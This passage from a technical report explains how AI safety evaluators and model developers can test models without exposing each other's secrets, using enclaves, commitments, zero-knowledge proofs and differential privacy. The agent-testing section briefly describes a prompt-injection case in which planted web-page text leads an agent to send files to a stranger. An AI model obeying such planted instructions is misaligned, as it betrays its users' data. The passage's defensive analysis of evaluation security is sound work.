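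Google faced much less risk because the weights stayed in its own cloud and the evaluators had no control over the hardware. The tests were double-blind in that neither side saw the other's secrets, but their guarantees were not equally strong. Bucknall and colleagues argue that inadequate protection makes it harder to trust an evaluator's independence or results.

Unlike an API, a properly working enclave keeps the evaluators' readable prompts out of the company's ordinary logs, and copying them deliberately would probably have required several people. The arrangement therefore protected the evaluators strongly against accidents and most individual employees, but only weakly against Google as an organisation.

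So the paper's phrase "cryptographic guarantees" is too strong for these tests. The encryption protected the prompts from people without access to the enclave, but confidence in the enclave depended largely on Google.

An evaluator can reduce that dependence without changing hosts by checking Intel's signed report for itself and insisting on a reproducible operating system. Google would then find it much harder to pass off an altered operating system, but the evaluator would still have to trust the hidden code and the physical server.

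### Moving the test to another company's machines

A host with no stake in the result would remove most of the conflict of interest. McCann-Sayles and Verma describe a trial with such a host, on a platform run by their company, Tinfoil, which sells confidential computing. The Brussels think tank Pour Demain used the platform to study GLM-5.1, a model with about 744 billion weights, on eight Nvidia H200 GPUs. The trial showed that the method works on a very large model. Pour Demain could already obtain the weights, however, so the trial did not show that a company would trust Tinfoil with a secret model.

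As well as collecting replies, Pour Demain used vllm-lens, an open-source tool from UK AISI that copies out the numbers a model calculates at each layer. An evaluator can use these numbers to look for problems that don't show up in the model's answers. But a tool like this has to run inside the company's inference code, which makes it harder for each side to hide its code from the other.

In the trial, confidential mode slowed GLM-5.1 by 6.7% in normal use and 33.4% with vllm-lens. The vllm-lens code itself caused little of the extra delay. A GPU can normally record the instructions for generating a token and then replay them with a single command. The tool can't read the model's layers during a replay, so it turns this feature off, and the processor has to send each instruction separately over the encrypted link. McCann-Sayles and Verma suggest sending instructions separately only for the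 layers under study. Even without that improvement, a test that normally takes three hours would take about four.

To use another host, the model owner has to send its weights outside its own data centres. The most experienced large hosts, Microsoft and Amazon, also compete with Google in AI. A small independent company avoids that conflict but may have fewer guards and engineers. Using its own cloud was probably the easiest way for Google to get its security staff to agree to a first test, which might not have happened otherwise.

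### Why the participants accepted the arrangement

Google wanted a result that outsiders would believe. Isaac and colleagues expect double-blind tests to be especially useful for government bodies and for sensitive subjects such as cybersecurity. Google also sells the cloud service that ran the tests, so it benefits commercially from showing that the service works.

The paper doesn't give AVERI's reasons for accepting the unchecked code, but the alternatives make the decision understandable. Google was not offering a copy of the weights, and an API would have exposed every prompt. The enclave was better than an API even if AVERI trusted Google no more than before. The case for technical protection has since grown stronger. Kang reports that in November 2026 the security company Dragos found evidence of privacy failures at several companies that run AI models for others, including on requests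 whose data was not supposed to be stored. OpenRouter, a service that connects users to such companies, then removed 125 of their connections from its no-retention option.

OpenMined says that scrutiny from AVERI and the Singapore institute made the system stronger, and that Google's security and legal staff took the unfamiliar technology seriously. All of these accounts come from people involved in the project. Trask is affiliated with both Google and OpenMined, although his co-authors on the paper include staff from AVERI, MLCommons and the Singapore institute.

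The 2026 arrangement is weakest on the benefit Google cared about most. Someone who suspects Google of training on test questions has little reason to be reassured by a report that Google verified, about software that outsiders could not fully inspect. For a benchmark whose main risk is an accidental leak, the arrangement is already a clear improvement on an API. If the questions could help someone make a weapon, the institute should insist on independent verification, a host that the company does not control, and either reading the hidden code or strictly confining it.

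## Checking the inputs and limiting what the answer reveals

Input privacy makes it harder to notice if the company swaps in a more cautious model, as described earlier. It also hides faults in the institute's test, such as mistakes in the answer key. The agreed program would still run normally in both cases. Each side therefore needs evidence about the other's input that it can check without seeing the input itself. Both also need to limit what a reader can work out from the result. In the worked multiplication, the institute could get the weight just by dividing the answer by its own input.

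### How each side could cheat

*Are You Getting What You Pay For?* (2025) defines model substitution as a provider secretly running a different model from the one it advertises. The usual motive is to save money. The provider charges for a large model but runs a smaller one, or a quantised copy that stores each weight less precisely. It can make the switch harder to detect by using the substitute for only some replies, or by recognising well-known benchmark questions and sending those to the advertised model.

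In a safety test, an organisation might switch the input to get a better score, or an engineer might upload last month's version by accident.

The company also has reason to worry about the institute's test. If 50 of the 1,000 answers in the key are wrong, a model that answers every question correctly scores only 95%. An evaluator that wanted an alarming result could write 10,000 questions, try them on similar public models and keep the 1,000 that produced the worst replies. The company could read a public benchmark and object to these flaws, but with a secret one it may see only the score.

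### Fixing the inputs in advance

A cryptographic commitment is a short string that fixes a piece of data without revealing it. According to *Certified in Theory, Broken in Practice* (Luck, Franzese-McLaughlin and colleagues, 2026), a commitment must be *hiding*, so that the string reveals nothing about the data, and *binding*, so that nobody can later pass off different data as the original.

A simple way to commit to data is to hash it together with a long random number. To open the commitment, the owner reveals both, and anyone can recalculate the hash. The random number stops anyone from finding the data by hashing guesses, as with the phone numbers earlier.

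The company can publish a commitment to its weights before the test. The program in the enclave recalculates the commitment from the weights it has loaded, and stops if the two differ. The institute learns that the enclave is testing the committed weights, but not what they are. The commitment should also cover the system prompt (the standing instructions that the model receives before each question), the safety filters and the settings for generating text, because the company can use any of these to alter the model's behaviour without changing the weights.

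The company has to commit to its model before it learns anything about the questions. Luck and colleagues show that a company that knows the test in advance can build a model that passes it but behaves very differently on new questions of the same kind. They conclude that an evaluator can't safely reuse a test once the model's owner has learned a substantial part of it.

The institute should commit to its questions, answers and marking rules too. Otherwise it could see a high score, drop the 100 easiest questions and report the score on the rest. If it commits to each question separately, an agreed expert can choose 30 at random and check whether they are any good, which the commitment alone doesn't show. If 10% of the questions are faulty, the expert has about a 96% chance of finding at least one (1 − 0.9³⁰). If only 1% are faulty, the chance falls to 26%. The company could do the check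 itself, but the institute would then have to retire the questions the company saw.

The company can also ask the institute to run the committed test on several public models. If all of them score much lower on it than on similar tests, the test may be broken.

### Matching the tested model to the one on sale

A commitment identifies the weights in the test, but customers also need to know that the commercial service uses those weights. If the company runs that service in enclaves, it can show this with the same method. *Attestable Audits* (2025) describes a system that runs a benchmark in an enclave and posts the signed result in a public registry, so users can check that they are talking to the audited model. Its prototype used Llama-3.1.

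Bicakci (2026), in *Making AI-Assisted Grant Evaluation Auditable without Exposing the Model*, proposes a similar record for public agencies that use a language model to help assess grant applications. For each application, the enclave signs a record that links the model, the scoring rules and the submitted text to the evaluation. If an unsuccessful applicant appeals, the appeal board could confirm that the agency used the declared model and rules. Bicakci stresses that the record does not show that the evaluation was fair or scientifically correct.

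An outsider can also test a service statistically, without the provider's help. In the method from *Auditing Black-Box LLM APIs with a Rank-Based Uniformity Test* (2025), the tester sends a prompt to the service and to a reference copy of the advertised model, collecting one reply from the service and several from the copy. The tester then scores the replies and ranks them by score. If both run the same model, the service's reply should be equally likely to take any position in the ranking. If the service's replies to many prompts cluster at one end, that suggests the provider has substituted a different model.

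*API-TAIL* (2026) looks for providers that substitute only a fraction of their replies. Its dataset contains 143,955 responses, including some from 26 honest services running two open models, Qwen3.8-27B and Gemma-4-31B-it. One audit takes 200 requests, less than $0.16 in API charges and two to eight minutes on a GPU.

Both methods require a copy of the model, so they suit open-weight models. An evaluator of a closed model has no copy, but the enclave does. The institute could buy replies to harmless prompts from the commercial service, and the agreed program could use the weights to score those replies before the weights are erased. The institute would have to send the prompts through an ordinary customer account, because a company that recognised them could answer with the right model even if it normally served customers a different one.

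Another option is to check a small part of the calculation behind each reply. In *Towards Verifiable AI with Lightweight Cryptographic Proofs of Inference* (2026), the provider commits to all the intermediate numbers and then reveals those along a few random paths from the output back to the input. With Llama-2-7B, making the commitment took 5.8 milliseconds and checking the proof took 12 milliseconds. A full proof with zkLLM, a system from 2024, took 388 seconds.

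A single check can miss cheating, but repeating it makes detection more likely. If each check had a 1% chance of catching a substitution, 500 independent checks would catch it 99.3% of the time. However, each proof includes the weights along its paths, so repeated checks gradually reveal a secret model.

### How a zero-knowledge proof of a score works

A zero-knowledge proof lets one party, the prover, convince another, the verifier, that a statement is true without revealing anything else. For example, the prover could show that "the model with this commitment passes 412 of these 500 items" while keeping the weights secret. An honest prover can always produce a valid proof, and a dishonest one has a negligible chance of getting a false statement accepted.

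Liang, Guo and colleagues (2026), in *zkLLMPoT*, set out a procedure for proving how well a language model does on chosen text:

1. The auditor chooses how to calculate the score and what range counts as a pass. The model owner turns the whole calculation into a fixed set of equations.
2. The owner commits to the weights.
3. The auditor chooses the test texts and sends them to the owner.
4. The owner runs the model, then commits to the score and to the output of every layer.
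5. Working backwards from the last layer, the owner proves that each layer's output follows from the previous layer and the committed weights.
6. The auditor checks that these proofs link up, and accepts if they do and the score is in the agreed range.

The auditor does not have to repeat the calculation. A model's multiplications are mostly very long sums, and a method called sumcheck can verify a sum without adding up its terms. Take the function f(x, y) = 1 + 2x + 3xy. If x and y can each be 0 or 1, it has four values: 1, 1, 3 and 6. The company claims that they add up to 11, and both sides calculate modulo 101, as before:

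1. The company adds up the two values of y but leaves x open, which gives the formula 2 + 7x. The institute puts in 0 and 1 and gets 2 and 9, which add up to 11.
2. The institute picks a random x, say 10, for which the formula gives 72. The company replies with f(10, y), which is 21 + 30y. Putting in 0 and 1 gives 21 and 51, which add up to 72.
3. The institute picks a random y, say 4, for which the new formula gives 141, or 40. It now needs only one value of the original function, f(10, 4), which the company proves using its commitment. This is also 40, so the institute accepts.

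If the company had claimed 12, it would have had to send a false formula in the first step. Two different straight lines cross at most once, so the false formula would give the wrong value for at least 100 of the 101 numbers the institute could pick. The company would have one more chance to avoid detection in the next step. Real systems pick from far more numbers, so a false claim is extremely unlikely to go undetected.

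*Infrastructure for Verifiable AI* (Xia, Xu and Wang, 2026) explains that checking a sum of 2ⁿ terms takes n rounds, so a billion terms need about 30. For non-linear steps such as softmax, the prover shows that each input-output pair appears in a table of correct pairs.

The formulas in the example reveal something about f, which in a real proof would depend on the weights. A zero-knowledge system therefore has to mask the formulas with random numbers.

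### How long the proofs take

Two systems published in November 2026, Sable and Anthropic's FlashProve, can handle proofs for models with tens of billions of weights or more. In April, Bicakci had judged that proofs for models of that size required too much computation.

The figures below for Sable and FlashProve come from *Sable* (Solberg, 2026), and the figure for DeepProve comes from Xia and colleagues. *ZKTorch* (2025) describes a general tool for turning ordinary model files into proofs, and *DiFR* (2025) gives the tool's speed.

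| System | Model | Proving time | Qualification |
|---|---|---|---|
| ZKTorch (2025) | Llama-2-7B | 2,646 seconds per token | – |
| DeepProve (2026) | Gemma 3, 270 million weights | 86 tokens per minute | Very small model, on ordinary processors |
| zkLLMPoT (2026) | 1.1 to 1.5 billion weights | 41–59 seconds for 512 tokens | Sum of separately measured steps, not one complete run |
| zkLLMPoT (2026) | 13 billion weights | 131 seconds for 512 tokens | As above |
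| Sable (2026) | Qwen2.5-32B | 92.5 seconds for 4,096 tokens | Not zero-knowledge |
| FlashProve (2026) | Llama 4 Maverick, 400.7 billion weights | About 111 tokens per second, in batches | Normally checks one output token per proof |

The systems use different hardware and security settings, so the table shows what is feasible rather than which system is best. Llama 4 Maverick also needs less computation than its size suggests, because it uses only about 16 billion of its weights for each token.

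FlashProve's one-token limit matters little for multiple-choice questions, because the model answers with a single letter. The system processes text in windows of 1,024 tokens, so if each question took up one window, a single H100 would need about two and a half hours for 1,000 questions. Written replies would take much longer unless the evaluator accepted the looser check FlashProve offers for whole replies.

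Producing a proof still takes far more computing than running the calculation it checks. *Anthropic open-sources FlashProve, its provable inference prototype for MoE models* (Pogorelec, 2026) puts FlashProve's overhead at 70 to 95 times. Solberg gives 41 to 50 times for Sable, or 6.4 cents for a request of 4,096 tokens.

Anthropic's *Progress on provable inference for large language models* (2026) presents such proofs mainly as a way for users to check which model answered them. A company could commit to one model, prove its test score and then attach a proof to each reply it sells, which would connect the test to the product without an enclave. Three problems remain:

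- **Rounding.** Both Sable and FlashProve replace the model with a version that uses only whole numbers, because ordinary calculations can give slightly different results on different hardware. Sable's version of Qwen2.5-32B chose the same most likely next token as the original in 86.3% of positions. On two standard benchmarks, its versions of two newer Qwen models stayed within 1.7 percentage points of the originals. A proved score applies only to the whole-number version, so the company has to sell that version or show that the difference is harmless.
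- **Leaks over time.** Sable isn't zero-knowledge, and Solberg estimates that about 20,000 proofs would expose a closed model's weights. FlashProve does hide the weights, but one commitment can serve at most 688,127 batches. That is plenty for a benchmark but not for a busy commercial service. *FlashProve-Next* (2026) is a design for commercial services that uses fresh random masks for each proof and so has no such limit.
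- **Bad tests.** A proof can show that the company calculated the score correctly, but not that the questions or answer key were sound.

### Why a proof does not protect the questions

Whoever computes the proof normally needs both the weights and the questions in readable form. In Liang and colleagues' procedure, the auditor gives the test to the model owner. The owner has already committed to the weights, so it can no longer change the model in response, but it has read every question.

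*PrivaDE* (2025), a system for buying and selling data, uses proofs in two ways, and both have the same limitation. One hides the model's weights but makes the data point public, and the other does the reverse. When the weights and the data point both have to stay secret, the system uses a separate MPC protocol. Bucknall and colleagues likewise found that two earlier proposals for auditing models with zero-knowledge proofs assumed that the owner could see the whole audit.

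A zero-knowledge proof therefore suits an evaluator that can write new questions for each test. It doesn't suit the secret biology benchmark.

The institute and the company could compute the proof inside an enclave. Anyone who broke into the enclave could then read the secrets but couldn't forge a score. For most tests, an enclave that checks both commitments is probably enough without a proof, since it gives similar evidence with much less computation.

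### What a score gives away

Suppose the biology benchmark has 500 items, each of which the model passes or fails. The total score has 501 possible values, so it carries at most log₂(501), or about 9 bits, of information. A list of the individual results carries up to 500 bits.

The company might agree to release only the total because it doesn't want anyone to know which dangerous tasks its model can do. But the institute could find out by differencing, the trick the teacher used in the age survey. If the total was 412 with all 500 items and 411 after removing one, the institute would know that the model had passed the removed item.

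Removing each item in turn would reveal the whole list in 501 runs. An evaluator could use fewer runs by removing carefully chosen groups, but would need at least 56, because 55 totals carry at most 493 bits, fewer than the 500 needed. Differencing can also happen by accident, such as when the institute finds a mistake in one question, deletes it and repeats the test. Differencing is less reliable when the model's replies vary from run to run.

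The number of bits an answer reveals does not measure how sensitive those bits are. For example, whether the model can help with one particular virus is a single bit, but it may be the information the company most wants to protect.

### Rules that limit repeated questions

A **query limit** restricts how many results the enclave will release. With one official run and one repeat, the two totals carry at most 18 bits. But a limit of two results would still allow someone to subtract 411 from 412, so the program should refuse a second run unless it uses exactly the same items or a substantially different set. The limit must also apply jointly to everyone who might compare results, since two evaluators with one run each could do the same subtraction.

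Tlaie and Farrell recommend restricting the types of query as well, so that evaluators can't probe for sensitive information. For a benchmark, both sides could approve a fixed list of scores before the test and allow no others.

A **minimum group size** prevents the program from releasing scores for very small groups of items. If the minimum is 20, the program would hide the score for a topic with three items. However, if the total is 412 and the visible topics add up to 409, a reader can tell that the model passed all three hidden items. To prevent this, the program would have to merge the small topic with another or withhold the total. A group that meets the minimum can also reveal individual results, because a score of 20 out of 20 shows that the model passed every item.

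The parties can also agree on a **fixed one-bit answer**, such as whether the model passed at least 400 items. The auditor-in-a-box prototype can restrict its output this way, and the accuracy certificates that Luck and colleagues describe reveal to the auditor only whether the error rate is below a threshold. The parties must fix the threshold beforehand, because an evaluator who could keep changing it would need only nine answers to find the exact total. A one-bit answer also hides useful differences, since a model that passes 399 items and one that passes 12 both get a "no".

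### What differential privacy protects

Differential privacy, the noise-adding method mentioned earlier, has an exact definition. Let D and D′ be two datasets that differ in one record, and let M be the noisy calculation. M satisfies ε-differential privacy if, for every such pair and every set S of possible answers,

Pr[M(D) is in S] ≤ e^ε × Pr[M(D′) is in S].

A smaller ε gives stronger protection. A standard way to protect a count is to add noise from a Laplace distribution centred on zero with a scale of 1/ε. If the records are the 500 item results and ε is 0.5, the published total will typically be off by about three. Whether the model passed or failed a given item changes the probability of any published total by a factor of at most e^0.5, or about 1.65. Someone who thought a pass and a fail equally likely before seeing the total could be at most 62% confident of either afterwards.

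Repeating the test weakens the protection, because the noise starts to average out. In the worst case, the values of ε add up, so after ten totals with an ε of 0.5 each, the combined ε is 5 and the same person could become over 99% confident. The parties therefore agree on a maximum combined ε, called the privacy budget, and the program stops answering when the evaluator reaches it.

This works well for individual records in user logs or hospital data, but not for a company whose secret is the entire model. The parties could treat the whole model as one record, but M would then have to give similar answers for every possible model. Replacing one model with another can change the score by as much as 500, so with an ε of 1 the noise would have a scale of 500 and obscure the result.

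Benchmarks have a similar problem, because differential privacy can hide the result for one item but not a fact that many items share. If 50 questions concern the same virus, the protection for that group is 50 times weaker. Adding noise to the score also doesn't hide the text of the questions, which is the institute's main secret.

### When a total is too little

The less a result reveals, the harder it is to tell whether the test worked. Suppose a model scores 25% on multiple-choice questions with four options. Its answers may be no better than guesses, it may have refused to answer most of the questions, or the marking program may have accepted "B" but rejected "The answer is B". An evaluator who sees only the total can't tell which of these happened, and neither can a company that wants to challenge a low score.

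The outside evaluator in the training-data study had the same problem, because a summary could not show why the keyword search had missed some documents. EleutherAI suggests that an owner could release a small sample of documents in such cases, so the evaluator can see what went wrong and improve the search.

The institute and the company have several other ways to compromise:

- **Practise in the open.** The institute can first run the program on public questions in the same format and look at every reply. This should expose most formatting and marking errors before the secret test begins.
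- **Count the types of failure.** The program can report how many replies were correct, wrong, refused or unreadable. For 500 items, these four numbers carry at most 24 bits, compared with 9 for the total alone, and they would explain many suspicious scores.
- **Show the replies to one side.** An evaluator who reads the replies, as AVERI's staff did in the Gemini pilot, can recognise a refusal or a misunderstood question.
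- **Match the openness to the danger.** Bucknall and colleagues suggest keeping evaluations private when they rely on information that affects national security and being more open about less sensitive ones. The institute could publish its arithmetic questions after the test but keep the biology questions secret.

The enclave can also save the item-by-item results in an encrypted file that neither side can open alone. If one side disputes the score, they can jointly open the file for an expert they both accept. The expert can then report, for example, that 40 replies were marked wrong because of a stray full stop, without revealing the questions to the company.

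## What current software does not support

The only published model evaluations in which two organisations protected real secrets from each other sent text prompts to a model small enough for a single GPU. Those tests ran on Google Cloud machines of a type that cannot be joined into a cluster, according to Google Cloud's *Supported configurations*. *When Agents Handle Secrets* (Forough, Kogias and Haddadi, 2026) found no established way to protect an AI agent from end to end. *Styx* (Zhao, Wang and colleagues, 2026) combined several organisations' data, but only in a research prototype.

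The table shows the state of the software in early December 2026. "Stand-ins" are public or invented material used in place of real secrets. "Not available" means the sources cited here describe no trial or product that covers the task.

| Task | Support | Evidence |
|---|---|---|
| Text prompts to a model on one GPU | Demonstrated with real secrets | Trask and colleagues, August 2026: the Gemini tests |
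| A model on several GPUs in one machine | Demonstrated with stand-ins | McCann-Sayles and Verma, 2026: the public model GLM-5.1 |
| A model spread over many machines | Not available | Google Cloud, second half of 2026: no clusters of confidential GPU machines |
| Closed inference code | Demonstrated with real secrets, but without a full check of the code | Trask and colleagues, August 2026 |
| Hidden architecture, with proof that the code is safe | Not available | Trask and colleagues, 2026: planned as future work |
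| Reading a model's activations | Demonstrated with stand-ins | McCann-Sayles and Verma, 2026: GLM-5.1 |
| Gradients and fine-tuning of a secret model | Not available | Gekker and colleagues, July 2026: current work mostly covers running models, not training them |
| Agents that need tools or a network | Not available | Forough and colleagues, May 2026 |
| Three or more parties | Demonstrated with stand-ins | Zhao and colleagues, April 2026: a hospital example |
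| Joining a model's logs with another organisation's records | Demonstrated with stand-ins | xD, 2025: group totals from public data |

### Models that need more than one machine

A weight usually takes up two bytes, so the H100 in the Gemini tests, with 80 GB of memory, can hold at most 40 billion weights, with no room left for the calculation. The larger of the two models tested in *Benchmarking Confidential GPU Inference on NVIDIA H100 under Intel TDX* (2026) has 30 billion weights, which gives a realistic idea of what fits.

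The big cloud providers' documented options are not much larger. Azure's confidential GPU machine has one H100 with 94 GB, according to Microsoft. Google Cloud's newest, generally available since 7 August 2026, also has a single GPU. Confidential Space, the service behind the Gemini tests, works only with H100s, according to Google Cloud's *Deploy workloads*. Customers have to rent these machines as either "spot" machines, which Google can reclaim at any time, or "flex-start" machines, which run for at most seven days. A long test therefore has to save its progress in encrypted form. Google doesn't allow its own AI chips, TPUs, in confidential machines. A model that normally runs on TPUs has to move to Nvidia chips for the test, and small differences in the arithmetic could change some of its replies.

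Nvidia's hardware can do more than current software supports. Nvidia's *Hardware-Rooted AI Security That Won’t Slow You Down* lists servers that protect up to eight GPUs together. *Benchmarking Confidential Computing Performance on NVIDIA Blackwell GPUs* (Asad and Grunseid, 2026) reports 183 GB of usable memory on each of eight B200s, or 1,464 GB in total. A model with a trillion weights would fit in that memory at one byte per weight but not at two.

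When a model is too big for one GPU, each GPU typically holds a slice of every layer. The GPUs calculate partial results, exchange them, add them up and move on to the next layer. In a model with 80 layers, this happens at least 80 times for every token. An enclave has to protect all the intermediate values that pass between the GPUs.

How well it does so depends on the link:

- **Between the CPU and a GPU**, the link is encrypted. The CPU encrypts the data and leaves it in a staging area called a bounce buffer, where the GPU collects it. Asad and Grunseid measured about 10 GB per second for each GPU. Using more CPU threads didn't help: with 16, transfers to the GPU fell to 5.4 GB per second.
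- **Between GPUs in one server**, protection depends on the generation of chip. The August 2025 release notes from Nvidia (2025) state that the eight-GPU mode on Hopper chips, which include the H100 and H200, leaves this traffic unencrypted. The GLM-5.1 trial used eight H200s, so its GPUs presumably exchanged readable data. The newer Blackwell chips, such as the B200, can encrypt it.
- **Between servers**, a network card would normally read and write GPU memory directly. Confidential mode blocks this because the card is outside the protected area. The data has to go from the GPU to its CPU, across the network to another CPU, and on to that CPU's GPU, passing through the slow bounce buffers at both ends.

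The last of these is the main technical reason many-machine enclaves are not ready. Asad and Grunseid explain the detour but did not measure its overhead. They expect a new standard, TDISP, to remove the detour by letting a processor include a network card in the protected area, but their system did not yet support TDISP.

Encryption inside a single server is a much smaller problem. Asad and Grunseid, who work for the confidential computing company Confidential.ai, ran MiniMax-M2.7, a model with 229 billion weights, with and without protection. Protection slowed it by 14.4% with replies of 256 tokens and by about 1% with replies of 2,048 tokens. The slowdown is larger for short replies because the GPUs exchange data for the whole prompt at once when they read it, but for only one token at a time when they write a reply. Protection therefore slows multiple-choice benchmarks the most, because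 they have long questions and one-letter answers. Poorly configured software causes an even larger slowdown, of 30% to 40%.

Hopper's eight-GPU mode also limits long tests because, as Nvidia warns, it can't replace its encryption keys while it is running. Each encrypted transfer uses up a number that must never repeat, and the program crashes when these numbers run out. The only way to get new keys is to restart the machine, after which both parties would have to check its attestation report and upload their secrets again.

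#### Leaks through timing

As with the instructions a CPU sends to a GPU, encryption doesn't hide the timing or amount of traffic between GPUs. After the 2024 pilot with GPT-2, Trask and colleagues warned that such patterns could reveal proprietary information in a large cluster.

The risk grows with the number of servers, because traffic between them crosses cables and switches that the host controls. A host could estimate how many layers the model has by counting the bursts of traffic for each token. Mixture-of-experts models send each token to only a few specialised parts of the model, which may be on different servers. The traffic then depends on the text, so it could also reveal something about the evaluator's questions. Sending dummy data at a constant rate would hide the pattern but use up capacity on a link that is already slow.

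To reduce leaks of this kind, Nvidia's confidential mode restricts precise GPU timers and switches off profiling tools. These restrictions make it harder to find out why a test is slow, and they don't stop the host from timing traffic on its own network.

#### What Nvidia has announced

In August 2025, Nvidia still limited the B200 to one GPU per confidential machine. Version 1.0.0 of its reference design, described in Nvidia's *Release Notes*, allows several, but only if all the GPUs in the server belong to the same confidential machine.

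The next step is the Vera Rubin NVL72, a rack that holds 72 GPUs and 36 CPUs. VentureBeat reports that it encrypts every link between them, and GamesBeat's *Nvidia Vera Rubin ramps into full production for fall launch* reports that production is under way. If the rack works as announced, it could hold a very large model without sending anything over an ordinary network, though a model spread over several racks would still have to send data over one. An evaluator should treat these claims as unproven until somebody outside Nvidia has tested the rack.

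### Looking inside a model

An evaluator who only sends text prompts doesn't need to know how the model is built, because the company can offer a standard interface. Hiding the architecture becomes a problem when the evaluator's code refers to parts of the model, such as "the output of layer 40". Trask and colleagues plan to use deferred execution, in which the evaluator writes instructions without seeing the model and the enclave later applies them to the real one.

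Zhao and colleagues built a prototype that applies a version of the confinement approach described earlier to closed inference code, which the evaluator can't read. The prototype is unsuitable for a large language model because it runs on Intel SGX, which can't protect data in a GPU's memory.

White-box work, which examines or changes a model's internals, raises a more basic problem. Evaluators may ask for activations (the numbers a model calculates at each layer), gradients (which show how a small change in one number would affect the result) or a fine-tuned copy (a version with further training). An enclave can calculate all of these, but the output itself may reveal the weights.

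Activations can reveal a model's weights because many of the model's steps are linear. Suppose a step turns two inputs into two outputs using a hidden table of four weights. If the inputs 1 and 0 produce 3 and 5, the first column of the table is 3 and 5. If the inputs 0 and 1 produce 2 and 7, the second column is 2 and 7, so two observations are enough to reveal the whole table.

A table with 8,192 inputs and 8,192 outputs has about 67 million weights, but an evaluator could in principle work them out from 8,192 independent observations. Each token provides one observation, so about 82 questions of 100 tokens could be enough. In practice, rounding errors make this harder, and the evaluator needs both the inputs and the outputs of the same linear step. Even without a direct attack, activations reveal far more than a score does. A model with 70 billion weights might have 80 layers that each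 produce 8,192 numbers per token. The activations for 1,000 questions of 100 tokens would take up 131 GB, almost as much as the model's 140 GB.

**Gradients** can expose either side's secrets. In the worked multiplication, the company's weight of 7 and the institute's input of 12 gave 84. Raising the input by 1 raises the answer by 7, so the gradient with respect to the input is the company's weight. Likewise, the gradient with respect to the weight is the institute's input, 12. Giving the first gradient to the institute or the second to the company would therefore reveal the other side's number. In a real model, each gradient combines many numbers, which makes the secrets harder to extract but doesn't remove them.

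**Fine-tuning** produces a new set of weights. If the institute received them, it would have a working copy of the company's model, and if the company kept them, it might be able to recover the institute's training examples. The tuned model therefore has to stay in the enclave for the agreed test and then be deleted. Asad and Grunseid found that training on eight protected B200s was only 10% to 13% slower in the standard number format, so computing power is not the obstacle.

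For all three, the safest approach is to do the analysis inside the enclave and release a narrow result. For example, if an evaluator wants to know whether a model can tell it is being tested, the agreed program could train a small classifier on the activations and report only its accuracy. This works for questions the evaluator can define in advance. It is much less useful for exploratory research, in which people look at some activations, form an idea and look again, because every new look would need approval and reveal a little more.

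### Agents that need tools

In an agent test, a model might have to find a security flaw in a program. The model writes a command, a computer runs it, and the model reads the result before choosing its next step. It may also need to search the web or use other companies' software.

Forough and colleagues point out that the enclave's protection does not cover these outside services. A web search could reveal the institute's secret task to the search company. An open connection would also give the company's hidden code a way to send the task out.

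An attestation report provides little reassurance here, because an agent's behaviour depends on the text it reads as well as on its code. If a web page contained planted instructions to send files to a stranger, the agent might obey them even though the enclave was running the approved software.

The two sides could put everything the agent needs inside the enclave, including the target program and saved copies of web pages. This should work for tests with a fixed set of tools, although both sides would have to approve much more software. They would also need a strong barrier between the agent's commands and the rest of the enclave. Forough and colleagues cite an experiment in which more than 75% of malicious commands succeeded against agents without such a barrier.

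Tests with several agents are even harder. If one agent passes work to a second in another enclave, and the second passes part of it to a third, the first needs evidence about both of the others. Forough and colleagues list this kind of combined attestation as an open problem.

### More parties and shared records

An enclave can serve more than two parties, since each one can check the attestation report for itself. It is harder for them to agree on rules for the result. In the example from Zhao and colleagues, several hospitals train a cancer model together. One may insist that its records make up a large enough share of the data to give it a say over the model, while another may want to limit its own share. Such demands can be impossible to satisfy together. For example, three hospitals can't each supply at least 40% of the data, because their shares would add up to at least 120%.

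Styx attaches each hospital's rules to its encrypted data. The software checks all the rules before it starts, then attaches new ones to its output, so the trained model carries restrictions too. The check can reveal that the rules conflict, but people still have to negotiate compatible rules.

MedPerf, MLCommons' platform for testing medical AI, reduces the need for joint rules. Trask and colleagues explain that it tests models on private data without the data leaving the institution that holds it. MedPerf suits questions that each hospital can answer separately, but not questions that require two hospitals' records about the same patient.

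OpenMined's question about late-night films and sleep likewise needs two organisations' records about the same person. Google Cloud's *From clicks to clusters* describes a similar use in advertising, where customers have used Confidential Space to connect their own records with Google's advertising services. The xD demonstration showed how to calculate group totals from two lists without an enclave.

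A model's logs are harder to use than a customer list because one person may have thousands of messages, some of which mention other people, and the analysis may need a second language model to interpret them. The two organisations may also identify the same person differently, for example by an email address and a patient number. Most of the necessary parts exist, but combining them would be new.

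### The PySyft vulnerability

GitLab's *CVE-2026-31220* (May 2026) describes a serious flaw in PySyft 0.9.5 and all earlier versions. Once somebody had approved an outsider's function, PySyft ran it inside the server's own process without isolating it. PySyft also didn't check the function for dangerous operations, such as opening files or running system commands. An attacker who got one harmful function past the reviewers could take over the server and get any other secrets on it.

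GitLab gives the flaw a severity of 9.8 out of 10. That may be slightly too high, because the score is for an attack that needs neither an account nor anyone's help, whereas the description mentions a low-level account and an approval. Changing those two settings in the standard formula gives 8.0, which still counts as "high".

GitLab listed no solution in June, and neither its entry nor OSV's *PYSEC-2026-546* (2026), an entry in another public database, lists a fixed version. OSV's entry, last modified on 1 July, gives 0.9.5 as the last affected version. The Gemini tests used version 0.10, which is outside the affected range, but that alone doesn't show that OpenMined has fixed the flaw. Organisations should not trust version 0.9.5 or earlier with real secrets, and should ask OpenMined how later versions isolate approved code.

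The flaw shows why human approval is not enough. Reviewers can miss harmful code, especially in long programs that rely on other people's packages. If a reviewer catches 95% of harmful submissions, an attacker who makes 20 independent attempts has a 64% chance of getting at least one through (1 − 0.95²⁰). Approval should decide which code may run, but the software should also isolate approved code to limit the damage when that decision is wrong. Each approved function should run in a separate process that can read only the named data and has no network access.

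An enclave doesn't remove this danger. It keeps the host out, but a harmful function that both sides have approved is already inside.

### Missing standards and tools

Many of the remaining gaps are in the shared tools that every joint analysis needs. Gekker and colleagues wrote in July 2026 that there was no common standard for checking different kinds of enclave. In October 2025, a firmware update changed the format of reports from AMD enclaves on Google Cloud, replacing version 3 with version 4, and Google warned that software written for the old version might stop working.

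Attestation can also fail when no one has tampered with the software. Google Cloud lists a known fault in which a GPU's measurements don't match the expected values, and advises customers to stop the machine completely and start it again. Tampering would also cause a mismatch, so if staff get used to restarting machines until the check passes, they may ignore a real attack.

Independent verification has improved since the Gemini tests, in which Google's own service verified the report. On 20 May 2026, Google added support for Intel's verification service, Intel Trust Authority, according to Google Cloud's *Confidential Space release notes*. An evaluator can now ask Intel to check the machine, but still has to trust Intel, which also makes the processor, and still can't reproduce Google's operating system.

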